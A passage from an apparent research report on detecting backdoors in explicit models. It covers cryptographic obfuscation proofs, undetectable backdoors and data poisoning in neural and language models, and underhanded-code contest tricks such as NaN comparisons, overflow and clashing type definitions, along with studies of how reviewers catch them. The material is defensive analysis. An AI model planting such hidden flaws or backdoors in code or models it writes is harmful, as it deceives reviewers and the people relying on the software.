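A Boolean circuit combines yes/no values through AND, OR and NOT gates, and the output of one gate can feed several others. Circuits are roughly as expressive as neural networks. Christiano and colleagues prove, under two cryptographic assumptions, that polynomial-size circuits are not efficiently defendable.

One assumption is that one-way functions exist. A one-way function is easy to compute, but given its output for a random input, no polynomial-time algorithm has more than a negligible chance of finding an input that produces that output. Multiplying two large primes is a likely example, because nobody knows a fast way for an ordinary computer to recover the primes from their product.

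The other assumption is that an efficient indistinguishability obfuscator exists. This program rewrites a circuit without changing its behaviour. If two circuits of the same size compute the same function, no polynomial-time algorithm can tell which one a rewritten circuit came from.

*Exact Non-Identity Check and Gate-Teleportation-Based Indistinguishability Obfuscation are NP-hard* (2025) explains that a slow obfuscator exists. It could list every circuit with the same size and function as the original and output the first in dictionary order. Equivalent circuits of the same size would all be turned into the same circuit, so none of the original author's choices would remain. An efficient obfuscator has to hide those choices without searching through every such circuit. Jain, Lin and Sahai constructed one from well-studied assumptions in 2021.

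The attacker starts with a pseudorandom function, which uses a secret key to compute answers that look random to anyone without the key. The attacker can also "puncture" the key at the trigger. The punctured key still gives the correct answer for every other input, but to someone who has only the punctured key, the answer at the trigger looks like a coin flip. The proof compares three circuits, all of which the attacker would obfuscate:

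| Circuit | Key inside the circuit | Answer on the trigger |
|---|---|---|
| Original | Full key | Computed from the key |
| Intermediate | Punctured key | Correct answer, stored separately |
| Altered | Punctured key | Wrong answer, stored separately |

The original and intermediate circuits compute the same function, so no fast algorithm can tell them apart after obfuscation. The intermediate and altered circuits differ only in one stored bit, and nobody with just the punctured key can tell whether that bit is correct. A polynomial-time defender therefore can't distinguish the original circuit from the altered one noticeably better than by guessing, even though the defender can see every gate. The alteration changes the output on only one of the 2^n inputs.

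The same defender would almost always win with unlimited time. For circuits with 100 inputs and descriptions of a million bits, the probability of losing is below 10^−22 by the description-length argument. The circuit contains enough information to identify the trigger, but no feasible computation can extract it.

Nobody is likely to hide a loan exception this way soon. *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) describes backdoors that rely on this type of obfuscation as far from practical. A strict limit on a model's length would probably rule them out for now. Knowing how the model was made would also help, because a defender with the full key could immediately see that the answer on the trigger was wrong.

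### Counting the questions in a decision tree

In a small decision tree, a rare exception needs a long path, and the defender can measure its length. If all inputs are equally likely, each new yes/no question on a path halves the share of inputs that continue along it, so a leaf at depth 3 receives one input in eight and a leaf at depth 30 receives about one in a billion.

Suppose the trees have at most 1,000 leaves and may disagree on at most a fraction ε = 2^−60 of inputs. Each input must then have at least 60 yes/no variables, because with fewer, changing the answer on even one input would exceed this limit. The trigger reaches one leaf in the original tree and another in the altered tree, and the two leaves give opposite answers. Any input that matches the trigger on every question along both paths reaches the same two leaves, so the trees disagree on it too. If the leaves are at depths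 a and b, at least a fraction 2^−(a + b) of all inputs match. This fraction can't exceed 2^−60, so a + b must be at least 60, and at least one of the leaves must be at depth 30 or more.

The deep leaf is almost never in the original tree. At most 1,000 of that tree's leaves are at depth 30 or more, and a random input reaches each of them with probability at most 2^−30. The attacker chose the tree before the trigger was drawn at random, so the trigger reaches one of these leaves with probability at most 1,000/2^30, or about 0.93 in a million. In all other cases, the trigger's leaf in the altered tree is at depth 31 or more.

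The defender therefore raises the alarm whenever the given input reaches a leaf at depth 30 or more. This misses the trigger less than once in a million games, and false alarms on the original tree are just as rare. The check takes about as long as running the tree once and needs no other test inputs.

It also doesn't require anyone to understand the tree. Even for a tree with a million leaves, far too many to read, the same calculation limits each type of error to about one in a thousand.

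Christiano and colleagues call this a mechanistic defence because it uses how the model computes its answer. There is no comparable check for neural networks in general. ARC is now looking for mechanistic explanations of how trained networks behave. *Returning to ARC*, by its executive director, gives this effort about a 10% chance of achieving its most ambitious goals in time.

The proof for trees assumes the inputs are uniformly distributed, or at least independent of one another. In real data, a shallow leaf can be rare. Hardly anyone would answer yes to "Is the applicant over 110 years old?", but if the tree asks this first, a leaf directly below it has a depth of only 1. Trees that compare numbers have the same problem, since they can single out a debt of 77 with just two comparisons, one with 76.5 and one with 77.5.

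A lender could instead count how many past applicants reached each leaf and flag anyone who reaches a nearly empty one. This check can fail when inputs are correlated. Suppose the original tree approves people with jobs, and the altered tree approves people with salaries. Many past applicants reached every leaf in both trees, and the trees agree about almost everyone, but they disagree about an applicant who has a job and no salary. Christiano and colleagues suspect that similar checks would work for other models that give a constant answer over each region of inputs, perhaps even when inputs aren't uniformly distributed, but they have not proved it.

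### The open case of Boolean formulas

A Boolean formula is a circuit in which each gate's output is used only once. An example is "(late > 3) or (debt > 50 and income < 20)", where each comparison counts as one yes/no input. Decision trees and rule lists can be written as Boolean formulas of moderate size. A program that stores an intermediate result and uses it in several places is more like a general circuit.

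Christiano and colleagues leave open whether polynomial-size Boolean formulas are efficiently defendable, and there seems to be no published answer. The defender can't rely on learning a replacement, because these formulas are not efficiently learnable if computing discrete cube roots, a problem in number theory, is hard. The proof for circuits doesn't settle the question, since it doesn't show that the obfuscated functions can be written as small formulas. The answer matters for explicit models because many readable sets of rules are formulas of this kind.

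An obvious defence would be to imitate the depth check. The defender would run the formula on the given input, record which values each gate receives, and raise the alarm if any gate receives a combination that is rare for random inputs. Thomas Read found an example that defeats this check. With four inputs, it looks like this:

```
original:  x3 and x4
altered:   (((x1 or (x4 and x2)) and x2) or (x4 and x3)) and x3
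```

The altered formula simplifies to "(x1 and x2 and x3) or (x3 and x4)". It differs from the original only when the first three inputs are yes and the last is no. The same pattern works for any number of inputs. With 61 inputs, the formulas disagree on only one of the 2^61 possible combinations of input values, yet every gate in the altered formula receives each combination of values it can take on at least one-eighth of them.

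This happens because each intermediate result can be yes in two ways. After input k, the result is yes if inputs 1 to k are all yes, or if input k and the last input are both yes. The second condition holds for a quarter of random inputs, so the gates often receive a yes. On the trigger, they receive the same yes because of the first condition, and checking the values alone can't detect the difference.

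In the simplified formula, the part that requires the first 60 inputs to be yes is separate, and random inputs satisfy it with probability 2^−60, so the check would catch the trigger. Christiano and colleagues suggest rewriting formulas before checking them, but they don't give a method that always finds a version that exposes the trigger.

### Clearing a model in advance

A defender who wins the game can flag a suspicious input while the model is in use, but can't necessarily tell beforehand whether the model contains a backdoor. For example, a program could approve any application whose cryptographic hash, a number that is easy to compute from the application but hard to reverse, equals a stored value. An auditor would see the comparison but might never find an application that satisfies it. If one arrived, a monitor could easily see that the comparison had succeeded. For a small decision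 tree, the auditor can at least list the deep leaves in advance, although a tree without a backdoor may have some too.

*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* shows how hard it can be to detect a backdoor in a model's weights in advance. In one construction, the malicious trainer uses the agreed data and training method and tampers only with the method's initial random numbers. Under standard cryptographic assumptions, no polynomial-time test can distinguish the resulting weights from honest ones, but the trainer can reverse the decision on any input by changing it slightly. In a loan application, changing the last few digits of the requested amount might be enough. The defender here has to judge the model without seeing a suspicious input, so this doesn't contradict the positive results for the game. A lender may still be able to neutralize the backdoor at run time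 by adding random noise larger than the trainer's changes to each application and averaging the answers, though a trainer who knows what noise to expect can prepare for it.

Bogdanov and colleagues give a stronger result for a class of deep networks whose first layer is random and fixed. Even an auditor with unlimited computing time can barely distinguish tampered networks from honest ones. The backdoor lets the trainer find very different inputs that produce almost the same output. Honest networks also have such pairs, but under standard assumptions nobody can find them efficiently. The trainer's advantage is mainly knowledge about the network that inspecting the weights doesn't reveal.

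These constructions hide the tampering among many random weights, which a short formula or program usually lacks. An auditor can also refit a formula's few constants to the data and check whether they match the originals. This makes the trick harder to use in an explicit model but doesn't rule out other kinds of backdoor.

### Poisoned data and malicious authors

The attacker's power also depends on how the backdoor gets into the model. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considers attackers who can influence a model only through the labels on its training examples. Their backdoor works only if the training procedure learns which inputs are triggers. A defender with the same number of labelled examples can run the same procedure and learn to recognize the triggers too. If the rule for recognizing triggers is too hard to learn, the attacker can't install the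 backdoor through labels.

Kaneko tested this on four language models with 7 to 9 billion parameters. When the secret was a single position in the input, the attack and the defender's reconstruction started to succeed together. Both did no better than chance when the secret was designed to be cryptographically hard to learn. The defender needs labelled examples of triggers, which can be very hard to get if the trigger is rare.

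The obfuscated circuits avoid this limit because the attacker writes the function directly. A person or language model writing a program can also do this, but someone who only mislabels data for a symbolic regression can't. An auditor therefore has more reason to worry about cryptographic tricks in a program from an untrusted author than in a formula that trusted software fitted to poisoned data.

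### Removing a trigger without finding it

A user can sometimes avoid a model's backdoor without knowing whether it has one. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) starts from an old technique for correcting faulty programs. Suppose a program that adds numbers gives a wrong answer for 30 + 12. The user can draw a random number, say 5, and have the program calculate 30 + 5 and 12 − 5, then add the results, 35 and 7. The program returns 42 without receiving the input that triggers the fault. By repeating this with other random numbers and taking the most common answer, the user can also overcome random errors on up to 15% of inputs.

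Goldwasser and colleagues extend this idea to models whose correct answers are close to a linear function or a polynomial. They query the model at random points related to the given input and combine the results. Another of their methods produces a complete clean model if the correct answers are close to certain functions of yes/no inputs, including shallow decision trees. The model can be an opaque network because only the task has to be simple.

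Their attacker may choose the trigger but not the distribution of inputs, which is the reverse of the game. They also guarantee something different, that the cleaned answers are accurate on average and practically the same whether or not someone tampered with the model. Any particular answer can still be wrong. If repayment followed something close to a linear score, a lender could use such a method to neutralize the exception for a debt of 77 without learning that the exception existed.

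## What underhanded programming contests showed

Underhanded code is source code that looks innocent and correct to a reviewer but does something harmful. Writing it is a simpler way to hide a backdoor in a program than using cryptography. Since 2004, several contests have invited programmers to write such code. Most of the entries are in C, which offers many more ways to hide harmful behavior than a formula does, so their relevance to explicit models depends on how many of the tricks would still work in a restricted language.

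### From vote counting to smart contracts

Daniel Horn ran the first of these contests, Obfuscated V, during the 2004 US presidential election. In *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest* (Horn, 2004), he credited the idea to an older contest for unreadable C code and to scandals over electronic voting. Entrants had to write a program that read a string of letters, one per ballot, and counted the votes for Kerry, Bush, Nader and others.

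Under the rules in Horn's *The Obfuscated V contest* (2004), a program could either always favour one candidate or count correctly until election day, 2 November, and then cheat. The judges read the entries and ran the one that looked most correct. It won if it miscounted, and otherwise they moved on to the next.

One entry had a variable whose name was a lowercase L. On election day the program set it to 104, and the line `total = total+l;`, which seems to add 1, added 104 instead. The author of this entry was Scott Craver, an information security professor at Binghamton University, who founded the Underhanded C Contest the following year. In the Underhanded C Contest's *FAQ*, he recalls being impressed that even a short program for counting characters could fail on a single day and so escape testing. His contest ran from 2005 to 2009 and from 2013 to 2015, with a new task each year:

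| Year | Apparent task | Hidden behaviour |
|---|---|---|
| 2005 | Process an image | Put an invisible fingerprint in it |
| 2006 | Count the words in a text | Run very slowly on one operating system |
| 2007 | Encrypt a file | Occasionally encrypt it weakly |
| 2008 | Black out parts of an image | Leave those parts recoverable |
| 2009 | Route airline luggage | Misroute a bag if a clerk types a certain comment |
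| 2013 | Measure the distance between two people in a social network | Give a wrong distance for the author's account |
| 2014 | Search posts for a government surveillance order | Reveal who is under surveillance |
| 2015 | Compare a nuclear warhead with a reference | Accept a fake |

Other contests followed for cryptography (2014 to 2018), JavaScript (2015) and Solidity (2017, 2020, 2022 and 2024). Solidity is a language for smart contracts, which are programs that hold and transfer money on a blockchain. Organizers also announced a contest in 2016 for Rust, a language that prevents many memory errors, but never published winners. The lack of winners is weak evidence that Rust is safe from underhanded code, since the contest may have attracted too little interest.

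### What the rules rewarded

The Underhanded C Contest gave more points to short, readable programs. *The 2005 challenge* explains that large source files look less innocent because an author can hide a lot in them. Entries also earned points if the flaw, once discovered, could pass for an honest mistake, and if the code still looked innocent with syntax highlighting.

A trick could rely on human perception as well as technical knowledge. The 2009 winner, described in the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge*, replaced swear words in the clerk's comments with censored versions. The list of replacements lacked one comma, and C joins two pieces of text that have no comma between them. This gave the word "damn" a nine-character replacement, which could push the end of a comment into the part of memory that marks a luggage record as deleted.

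The hidden behaviour usually had to be rare. The Underhanded C Contest's *The 2013 Challenge* counted a flaw as rare enough if it appeared by chance at most 1% of the time. The probability that n random tests all miss a flaw with rate p is (1 − p)^n, so about 300 tests would have a 95% chance of triggering a flaw with a 1% rate. According to the contest's *This year's challenge*, the rate could be as low as 0.01% in 2007. That would take about 30,000 tests, and the tester would also have to recognize a weakly encrypted file.

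Entrants to the 2015 contest had to put their explanations in a separate file, so that the judges could first read the code without knowing the trick. Finding the trick unaided was difficult. Craver (2014), in *2013 Winners*, noted that some of that year's entrants had given no hints about their bugs. In the Underhanded C Contest's *Review of the 2014 Challenge*, he describes staring at one very short and readable entry without finding the flaw. The flaw was outside the code he was reading, in a function mentioned in a comment at the top. That function downloaded the user's profile picture when it archived a post, so a user who hosted the picture could watch for the download and learn of the surveillance.

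These contests prove that short, readable malicious code exists, but they don't measure how often it gets past a reviewer. Unlike real reviewers, the judges knew that every entry was supposed to contain a flaw, and they published no count of the flaws they found without help. For Underhanded C, they also described mostly the best entries, so weaker attempts are largely missing from the record. Measuring how well reviewers catch such code requires controlled experiments.

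### The nuclear-inspection challenge

The 2015 task is the closest to a small learned formula. The Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works to reduce the danger from weapons of mass destruction, sponsored the contest and helped design the problem.

Two countries have agreed to destroy nuclear warheads, and inspectors have to confirm that each warhead is real. They could measure its gamma-ray spectrum, a list of radiation counts at different energies, but the spectrum would reveal secrets about the weapon's design. The countries therefore agree on a program that compares the spectrum with a trusted reference and outputs only "yes" or "no".

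Entrants had to write the function that makes this comparison. It receives two lists of numbers, their length, and a threshold for how similar they must be. They could use any formula with a good justification, and common formulas earned more points. The function had to reject ordinary mismatches but accept a fake under unusual conditions that the inspected country could create.

One common formula is cosine similarity. For test counts t and reference counts r, it is

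(t₁r₁ + t₂r₂ + …) / √((t₁² + t₂² + …) × (r₁² + r₂² + …))

The result is 1 if the two spectra have exactly the same shape, and 0 if they have no energies in common. Like the loan rule, the function calculates a score from a few measurements and compares it with a threshold. Symbolic regression could plausibly produce such a formula.

### Undefined results

The contest received over 40 entries, and about a third used NaN, the computer's value for an undefined result. A function that rejects only scores below the threshold will accept NaN, just as one version of the loan program would.

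*Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) gives Peter Eastman's entry as a good example. The entry subtracts the normal background radiation from each count and replaces negative results with zero, which is a sensible precaution. It then correlates the two spectra, dividing by their standard deviations. If no count exceeds the background, every value becomes zero, the correlation is 0/0, and the function reports a match.

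Random testing would be very unlikely to reveal this. Suppose the spectrum has 100 counts, and each is equally likely to be above or below the background when no warhead is present. The probability that none is above it is one in 2^100, or about one in 10^30. The country being inspected would have to find a way to suppress the readings.

Craver did not shortlist most of the NaN entries. Some assumed that the host country could tamper with the input directly, while others relied on contrived conditions or on a division with no check for zero, which experienced C programmers tend to notice. An unguarded division is a much less useful warning sign in learned formulas, because symbolic regression often produces them, as in the SRBench formula for gravitation.

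Philipp Klenze's entry was subtler. It uses a standard statistical test based on the Poisson distribution, which gives the probability of each possible count when events occur at random at a fixed average rate. To find the probability of a count k, the program raises the average to the power k and divides the result by the product of all whole numbers from 1 to k. For large counts, both the power and the product are enormous, although their ratio may be of ordinary size.

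Once a count reaches 1,686 in a place where the reference is near zero, the power is too large even for the program's extended number format, which goes up to about 10^4932 on ordinary PCs. The program stores infinity, then subtracts infinity from infinity and gets NaN. This trigger is physically realistic, unlike most that depend on extreme values. Klenze's formula is mathematically correct, so a reviewer has to think about the size of the intermediate results to find the flaw. An equivalent formula that added logarithms instead of multiplying huge numbers would not have this problem.

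### Two files and one name

*Faking Fissile Material* (Åkesson, 2016) describes Linus Åkesson's winning program, which has only 66 lines of source code. The program checks that the test spectrum contains enough energy, smooths both spectra to bring out their peaks, and compares them by cosine similarity.

The flaw is that the main file and the comparison file use different definitions of `float_t`. The main file takes its definition from a small file that accompanies the program, which makes `float_t` a 64-bit number and has a comment about the desired precision. The comparison file uses the definition in C's standard mathematics library, where `float_t` is normally a 32-bit number. Neither file includes both definitions, so the compiler reports no conflict.

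The main file therefore passes 64-bit numbers to a function that reads memory 32 bits at a time. The function takes each count for two separate numbers, and because it expects a fixed number of values, it stops halfway through the spectrum. For whole-number counts below about a million, one of the two numbers is always zero and has no effect on the comparison. The other is a heavily compressed version of the count:

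| Actual count | Number used in the comparison |
|---|---|
| 10 | 2.56 |
| 100 | 3.39 |
| 1,000 | 4.48 |
| 10,000 | 6.11 |

Suppose one spectrum has counts of 10 and 1,000 in its first two places, and another has 1,000 and 10. Their cosine similarity should be 0.02, but after the compression it is 0.86. The compression gives the peaks that should distinguish a real warhead from a fake much less influence on the comparison. Material that shows up only in the second half of the spectrum can satisfy the energy check without affecting the comparison.

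A reviewer could easily miss this because each file makes sense by itself. The comparison function's declaration is identical in both places, but `float_t` means something different in each. A reviewer who assumed that the name had one meaning would miss the problem even after getting every calculation right. Craver found nothing suspicious in the rest of the code.

Åkesson's 2013 entry had a similar weakness. He explains in *Obsessbook* that the bug came from the interaction between two modules and that reviewers who examined them separately would be unlikely to find it. Two entries in 2014 had also used tricks similar to the winning one. In one, two files used different memory layouts for the same data, and in the other, a function treated a 64-bit number as a 32-bit integer.

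The lesson for reviewers is to check the definitions that different parts of a system share. This applies to explicit models too. If the loan formula expects debt in thousands of dollars but another program supplies it in dollars, the formula will give wrong decisions even though its text is correct.

The Nuclear Threat Initiative's *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* pointed out that arms control had no standards for writing or reviewing such code. Inspectors had ways of checking hardware, such as choosing devices at random, but there was no consensus on how to develop trusted software.

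### Triggers in the data and in the environment

Craver distinguished two kinds of trigger. A data trigger is an unusual spectrum, as in the entries by Eastman, Klenze and Åkesson. An environment trigger is a change to the computer running the program. Two entries misbehaved if the number of available processors changed during the calculation, and Ghislain Lemaur's entry depended on the user ID of a log file's owner.

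The judges tended to prefer data triggers because they require no assumptions about access to the computer. But inspection experts told them they could not rule out tampering with the environment, since the host country might have physical custody of the machine. Some data triggers were also unrealistic, such as a spectrum with counts too large for an ordinary integer.

A pure formula has no environment triggers because it only applies arithmetic, standard functions and comparisons to its inputs. It cannot check the date, read a file or remember an earlier calculation. The election-day programs in Obfuscated V could not be written as pure formulas unless the date were one of the inputs. This is a major advantage for an auditor, who only has to consider the listed inputs.

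The environment can still affect those inputs. Stephen Oman's program divides each count by the length of the scan, which it calculates from the start and end times. If someone sets the clock back during the scan, the length is negative and so are all the results. The program then checks the area under each peak against a lower and an upper limit by testing that two ratios, the lower limit divided by the area and the area divided by the upper limit, are at most 1. With limits of 90 and 110, an area of −100 gives ratios of about −0.90 and −0.91, and both pass.

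An auditor who assumes that areas are never negative could prove these checks correct, but the proof would not apply once the clock had changed. The system therefore has to enforce any input range that a proof assumes, for example by rejecting negative values before they reach the formula.

### Which tricks work in a pure formula

Craver's report discusses the code of 11 entries. The table shows which of their tricks would still work if the language allowed only pure formulas and one number format.

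| Entry | What the trick depends on | Works in a pure formula? |
|---|---|---|
| Eastman | Zero divided by zero | Yes |
| Klenze | Numbers too large to store | Yes |
| Dolan | Lost precision | Yes |
| Oman | Negative values that pass both limits | Yes, if inputs can be negative |
| Lospinoso | A missing letter that turns a test for infinity into a sine | Only if a number can count as "yes" |
| Dunphy | An error flag that changes only in a copy | No |
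| Egan | Unreadable input that leaves a NaN in memory | No, but the code that reads the input could still have the flaw |
| Lemaur | A log message that overwrites a number in memory | No |
| Stewart | Memory that runs out after repeated tests | No |
| Bierner | Text that the computer runs as instructions | No |
| Åkesson | Two definitions of the same name | No |

Six of the 11 tricks do not work in a formula, because a formula has no pointers (variables that hold a location in memory), macros (abbreviations that the compiler expands before it processes the code) or memory that one part of a program can overwrite. The other five include the most popular trick, NaN.

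Stephen Dolan's entry shows how lost precision can hide a mismatch. It squares the difference between the two spectra at each energy and adds up the squares. To keep one bad reading from spoiling the comparison, it then subtracts the largest square and takes the square root of the rest. If the differences are 1,000,000,000, 5 and 5, their squares are 10^18, 25 and 25, so the result should be the square root of 50, or about 7.1.

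But near 10^18, the numbers that the 64-bit format can represent are 128 apart, so adding each 25 to 10^18 gives 10^18 again. Subtracting the largest square then leaves zero, which the program scores as a perfect match. Craver thought a spectrum with such a huge first value was unrealistic, but the inputs to a learned formula for some other task could differ in size by that much.

Interval arithmetic can help with all three formula tricks that need no negative inputs. In Eastman's formula, it would show that the divisor can be zero. In Klenze's, it would show that an intermediate result can exceed the largest number the format can store. In Dolan's, with every bound rounded outwards, it would give a final distance between 0 and 16 instead of exactly 0. With a threshold of 5, the program could then report the result as uncertain.

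These checks are much easier to apply to a formula than to a C program that uses pointers and files. A restricted language could also treat every NaN as "no match". The auditor would still have to confirm that the deployed program does this.

Reviewers can also miss wrong constants. Lena Olson's 2014 entry was supposed to round times to the nearest second, but one of its limits was 5,000,000 microseconds instead of 500,000. The extra zero made the rounded time depend on whether a post was under surveillance. The error is hard to see, but a reader who knows that half a second is 500,000 microseconds can check the limit. A constant such as 0.83 in a learned formula usually has no obvious correct value to check it against.

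Programs, unlike formulas, can contain comments that mislead a reader. In the JavaScript contest, some entrants put a link to a popular programming forum next to strange code. The organizer noted that he found it easier to skip code with a good comment above it. A reviewer can avoid this influence by first reading the program with its comments removed.

### Errors in the method itself

John Meacham won the 2008 Underhanded C Contest with a 55-line program for blacking out parts of an image. The contest's 2008 page, *This year's challenge*, explains that the image file stores the brightness of each pixel as text. Meacham's program replaces every digit in the chosen area with a 0, so 7 becomes 0 and 200 becomes 000. The area looks completely black, but the number of zeros still shows whether each pixel was dark or bright.

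This program doesn't rely on tricks with pointers, macros or types. A reviewer could understand every line and still miss the leak, because the error is in the method. The same method would leak the same information in any language that can read and write text, even a memory-safe one.

Many winners of the cryptography contest relied on errors of this kind. Adam Caudill and Taylor Hornby started the contest after Caudill asked in August 2014 whether anyone would be interested (Caudill 2015, *On the Underhanded Crypto Contest*). One task in a smaller contest at the 2015 Def Con hacker conference was to change the encryption program GnuPG so that it leaked a user's private key.

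The winning change affected digital signatures. Each signature needs a fresh random number, and Hornby, in *Underhanded Crypto Contest*, explains that an attacker can recover the private key if this number isn't random enough. When GnuPG has to reject its first choice, it replaces only 32 bits and keeps the rest. According to Crypto Village's *Underhanded Crypto Contest Results*, the winner set the rejected number to zero, supposedly to keep it secret. This also erased the random bits GnuPG would have kept, so the replacement had only about 32 random bits.

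A reviewer without specialist knowledge would probably approve of erasing a secret number. Wheeler (2020) concludes in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* that specialists need to review code in fields such as cryptography.

The nuclear-inspection problem has similar risks. Cosine similarity measures only the shape of a spectrum, so it stays at 1 if every count falls to a tenth of its reference value. If a country could make fakes with the right spectrum from a tenth of the material, a program that used cosine similarity alone would accept them. Dolan's program ignores the largest difference even when its arithmetic is exact, so a fake with a single missing peak could pass.

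Both weaknesses would remain even in the simplest possible formula. A proof that the program computes cosine similarity correctly would not reveal the first, because the flaw is the choice of cosine similarity. To find it, the auditor has to compare the formula with what the inspectors need to know.

### Five countermeasures

David Wheeler, who works on software security at the Institute for Defense Analyses, a US nonprofit, tested whether simple precautions could catch underhanded code. He used 40 entries from Obfuscated V, including two of his own, and excluded one other published entry because its code contained no attack.

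Wheeler chose five countermeasures and recorded which entries each would catch. Several entries appear in more than one row.

| Countermeasure | Entries caught |
|---|---|
| Turn on many of the compiler's warnings | 15 |
| Strictly limit the use of macros | 9 |
| Ban names that confuse l with 1 or O with 0 | 8 |
| Run the program with a tool that detects memory errors | 5 |
| Colour and reformat the code to expose instructions inside comments | 2 |

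Together they caught 30 of the 40 entries. The compiler should have caught one more, whose indentation misled the reader about which lines belonged to a loop, but missed it because of a bug in its indentation check, which Wheeler reported to the developer. He judged that six of the remaining nine entries would look suspicious to a reviewer, for example because they contained a lot of unnecessary repetition.

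Of the three remaining entries, one filled in only part of a table, another treated numbers of one type as if they were another type, and the third checked twice for a lowercase n instead of once for n and once for N. All three were from the group that always miscounts under some conditions, so good tests would expose them. The countermeasures caught seven of the nine entries that cheated only on election day, and Wheeler considered the other two suspicious.

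These results are encouraging, but they probably overstate how well the countermeasures would work against a new attack. Wheeler chose the countermeasures after studying the entries, as he acknowledges, and the entrants had not tried to evade them. He alone decided what looked suspicious, and he already knew where the flaws were. For some programs, he predicted the memory tool's results from how it works instead of running it.

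Wheeler also did not apply the countermeasures to a comparable set of programs without underhanded code, so the study provides little evidence about false alarms. Many entries contained unrelated mistakes that produced warnings. He counted an entry as caught by the compiler only if a warning directly revealed the underhanded code, but a reviewer who didn't know which code was underhanded would have to investigate the other warnings too.

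The contest's own explanations were wrong, misleading or inconsistent with the code for four of the 41 published entries. In one entry, the votes went wrong because of a misused remainder operation, not the confusion between O and 0 given in the explanation. Even people who knew that a short program was malicious, and had a hint about the reason, could misidentify the flaw. Wheeler found the flaws easier to spot with practice, but he also reviewed the entries in roughly descending order of difficulty.

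A restricted language would have prevented many of these attacks without anyone having to detect them. By Wheeler's classification, 18 of the 40 entries relied on memory errors, macros, code inside comments or a confusion between assigning a value and testing for equality, none of which a pure formula allows. Another seven relied on similar-looking characters, which would be harmless if the language fixed the names of variables in advance. But a rule list could still contain the condition "vote = n or vote = n", and Wheeler suggests that compilers should warn about such repetition.

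### How Solidity's designers responded

Removing a dangerous construct from C is difficult because so much existing software depends on it. Solidity was newer, and its designers were closely involved in its contests. Its two co-leads were among the five judges in 2020. According to that year's contest announcement, the judges would see the entries without their authors' names. In *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2022*, Heintel (2022) lists uncovering flaws in the language's design among the contest's aims.

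In the 2017 contest, many entries gave a variable the same name as one of Solidity's built-in values, such as `now`. A reader would assume that `now` meant the current time, but the author could give it any value. This resembles Åkesson's trick with `float_t`. Wheeler reports that Solidity's designers had added warnings about such names shortly before the contest and were working on a more complete solution afterwards. They also found that a solver could automatically detect some of the attacks.

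Another common trick exploited the record a contract can keep of the money it has received. There were ways to send the contract money without running the code that updates this record, so the record and the actual balance could differ. A reviewer might reasonably assume that they always agree. The designers considered this difficult to fix through the language alone, since the problem came from how payments worked on the blockchain.

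One entry in 2020 exploited a compiler bug that version 0.7.3 fixed (Solidity, 2020), but the judges found the code suspicious. In the 2013 Underhanded C Contest, Gaëtan Leurent had used a related method that did not need a compiler bug. According to Åkesson, his program contained a visible safety check, but the compiler removed it because the surrounding code broke C's rules. In both cases, reading the source code was not enough to know what the computer would do. A small language with precise rules makes such surprises less likely, but an auditor still needs to trust or check the software that runs the formula.

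Another 2020 entry exploited contracts that their owners can upgrade after an audit. The judges said that earlier audits were worthless unless someone also checked every upgrade and the contract's initial setup. The same applies to a lender who fits a new formula to new data every month. The auditor can check which constants and terms have changed, but the proof for last month's formula does not automatically cover this month's.

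## How well people find planted flaws and predict what explicit models do

Experimenters measure how often harmful code gets past reviewers by planting a flaw in a program and counting how many reviewers find it. Most of these experiments used ordinary software. Other experiments tested how well people can predict what a readable model or set of rules will do, usually without a planted flaw.

### A voting program built for review

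The closest test of the case for explicit models involved Pvote, a program that displays the ballot on a voting machine and records the voter's choices. Ka-Ping Yee designed it to be easy to review. It has 460 lines, while the software of the Diebold AccuVote TS, a commercial machine, has more than 31,000 (Yee, *Extending prerendered-interface voting software to support accessibility and other ballot features*).

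Pvote can be so short because election officials prepare in advance most of what the voter sees and hears. They put the images, the sounds and the response to each touch of the screen into a file called the ballot definition, and Pvote only carries out what the file specifies. The ballot definition is effectively a program in its own restricted language. Someone still has to review it, so part of the complexity has only moved from Pvote to the file. But officials can publish the file before the election, and anyone can try it on an ordinary computer.

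Yee also tried to reduce how much a person has to check. Suppose a ballot has 50 candidates, and the machine speaks each name in four different messages, such as "Candidate X has been selected". If every message were a separate recording, a reviewer would have to listen to 200 recordings to be sure that none contained the wrong name. If the names and the rest of the messages are separate clips, the reviewer only has to listen to 54, and a computer can check that every message uses the right ones.

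Pvote is written in Pthin, a small subset of Python. Pthin is deterministic, so a program always does the same thing given the same inputs. It can't start cheating on election day, as some entries in Obfuscated V did, unless the date is one of its inputs. But unlike a pure formula, Pvote has to store which candidates a voter has already selected, so a flaw could depend on the order of the voter's actions.

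Yee's 2007 dissertation describes a review in which experts searched Pvote for three planted flaws, which Yee classed as easy, medium and hard. The reviewers knew that a particular 100-line region contained at least one flaw. After about 20 reviewer-hours, several experts had found the easy flaw, one had found the medium flaw, and none had found the hard one.

David Wagner, a computer scientist at Berkeley who ran the study with Yee, later invited the public to look for a planted flaw in a reconstructed version of the program. His invitation, reproduced in Financial Cryptography's *The Ka-Ping challenge* (2013), also explains the conditions of the original study. The reviewers had an explanation of Pvote's design and a detailed written argument for its security. They could also question Yee and Wagner, but were supposed to treat them as adversaries who might lie. To save time, the two promised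 to answer truthfully when the reviewers could in principle check the answer mechanically or in an independent source, as with questions about how Python works.

Yee and Wagner chose a flaw that would not show up in the test officials commonly run before an election, in which they usually cast at least one vote for each candidate and check the totals. The reviewers therefore had to find the flaw by reading the code, much as an auditor would have to find a rare trigger.

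These conditions were far better than most auditors could expect. Twenty hours for 100 lines is 12 minutes per line. At that pace, the 750,000 lines estimated earlier for a small language model would take about 80 years to read instead of two, and the reader might still miss a flaw as subtle as the hard one.

The attackers were also at a disadvantage because they had to add their flaws to code that Yee had already written to be as secure and verifiable as possible. Someone who planned a backdoor from the start could have designed the whole program around it, as Linus Åkesson did with his two definitions of `float_t`.

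The experiment used only three flaws in one program, too few to estimate a detection rate reliably. But it shows that experts can miss a flaw in a short program written in a restricted language, even when they know roughly where to look. A learned formula with 20 nodes is much smaller than even the 100-line region, so the result may be too pessimistic for such formulas. It is probably more relevant to the programs that systems such as AlphaEvolve produce, which can be hundreds of lines long.

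### Student attackers and auditors

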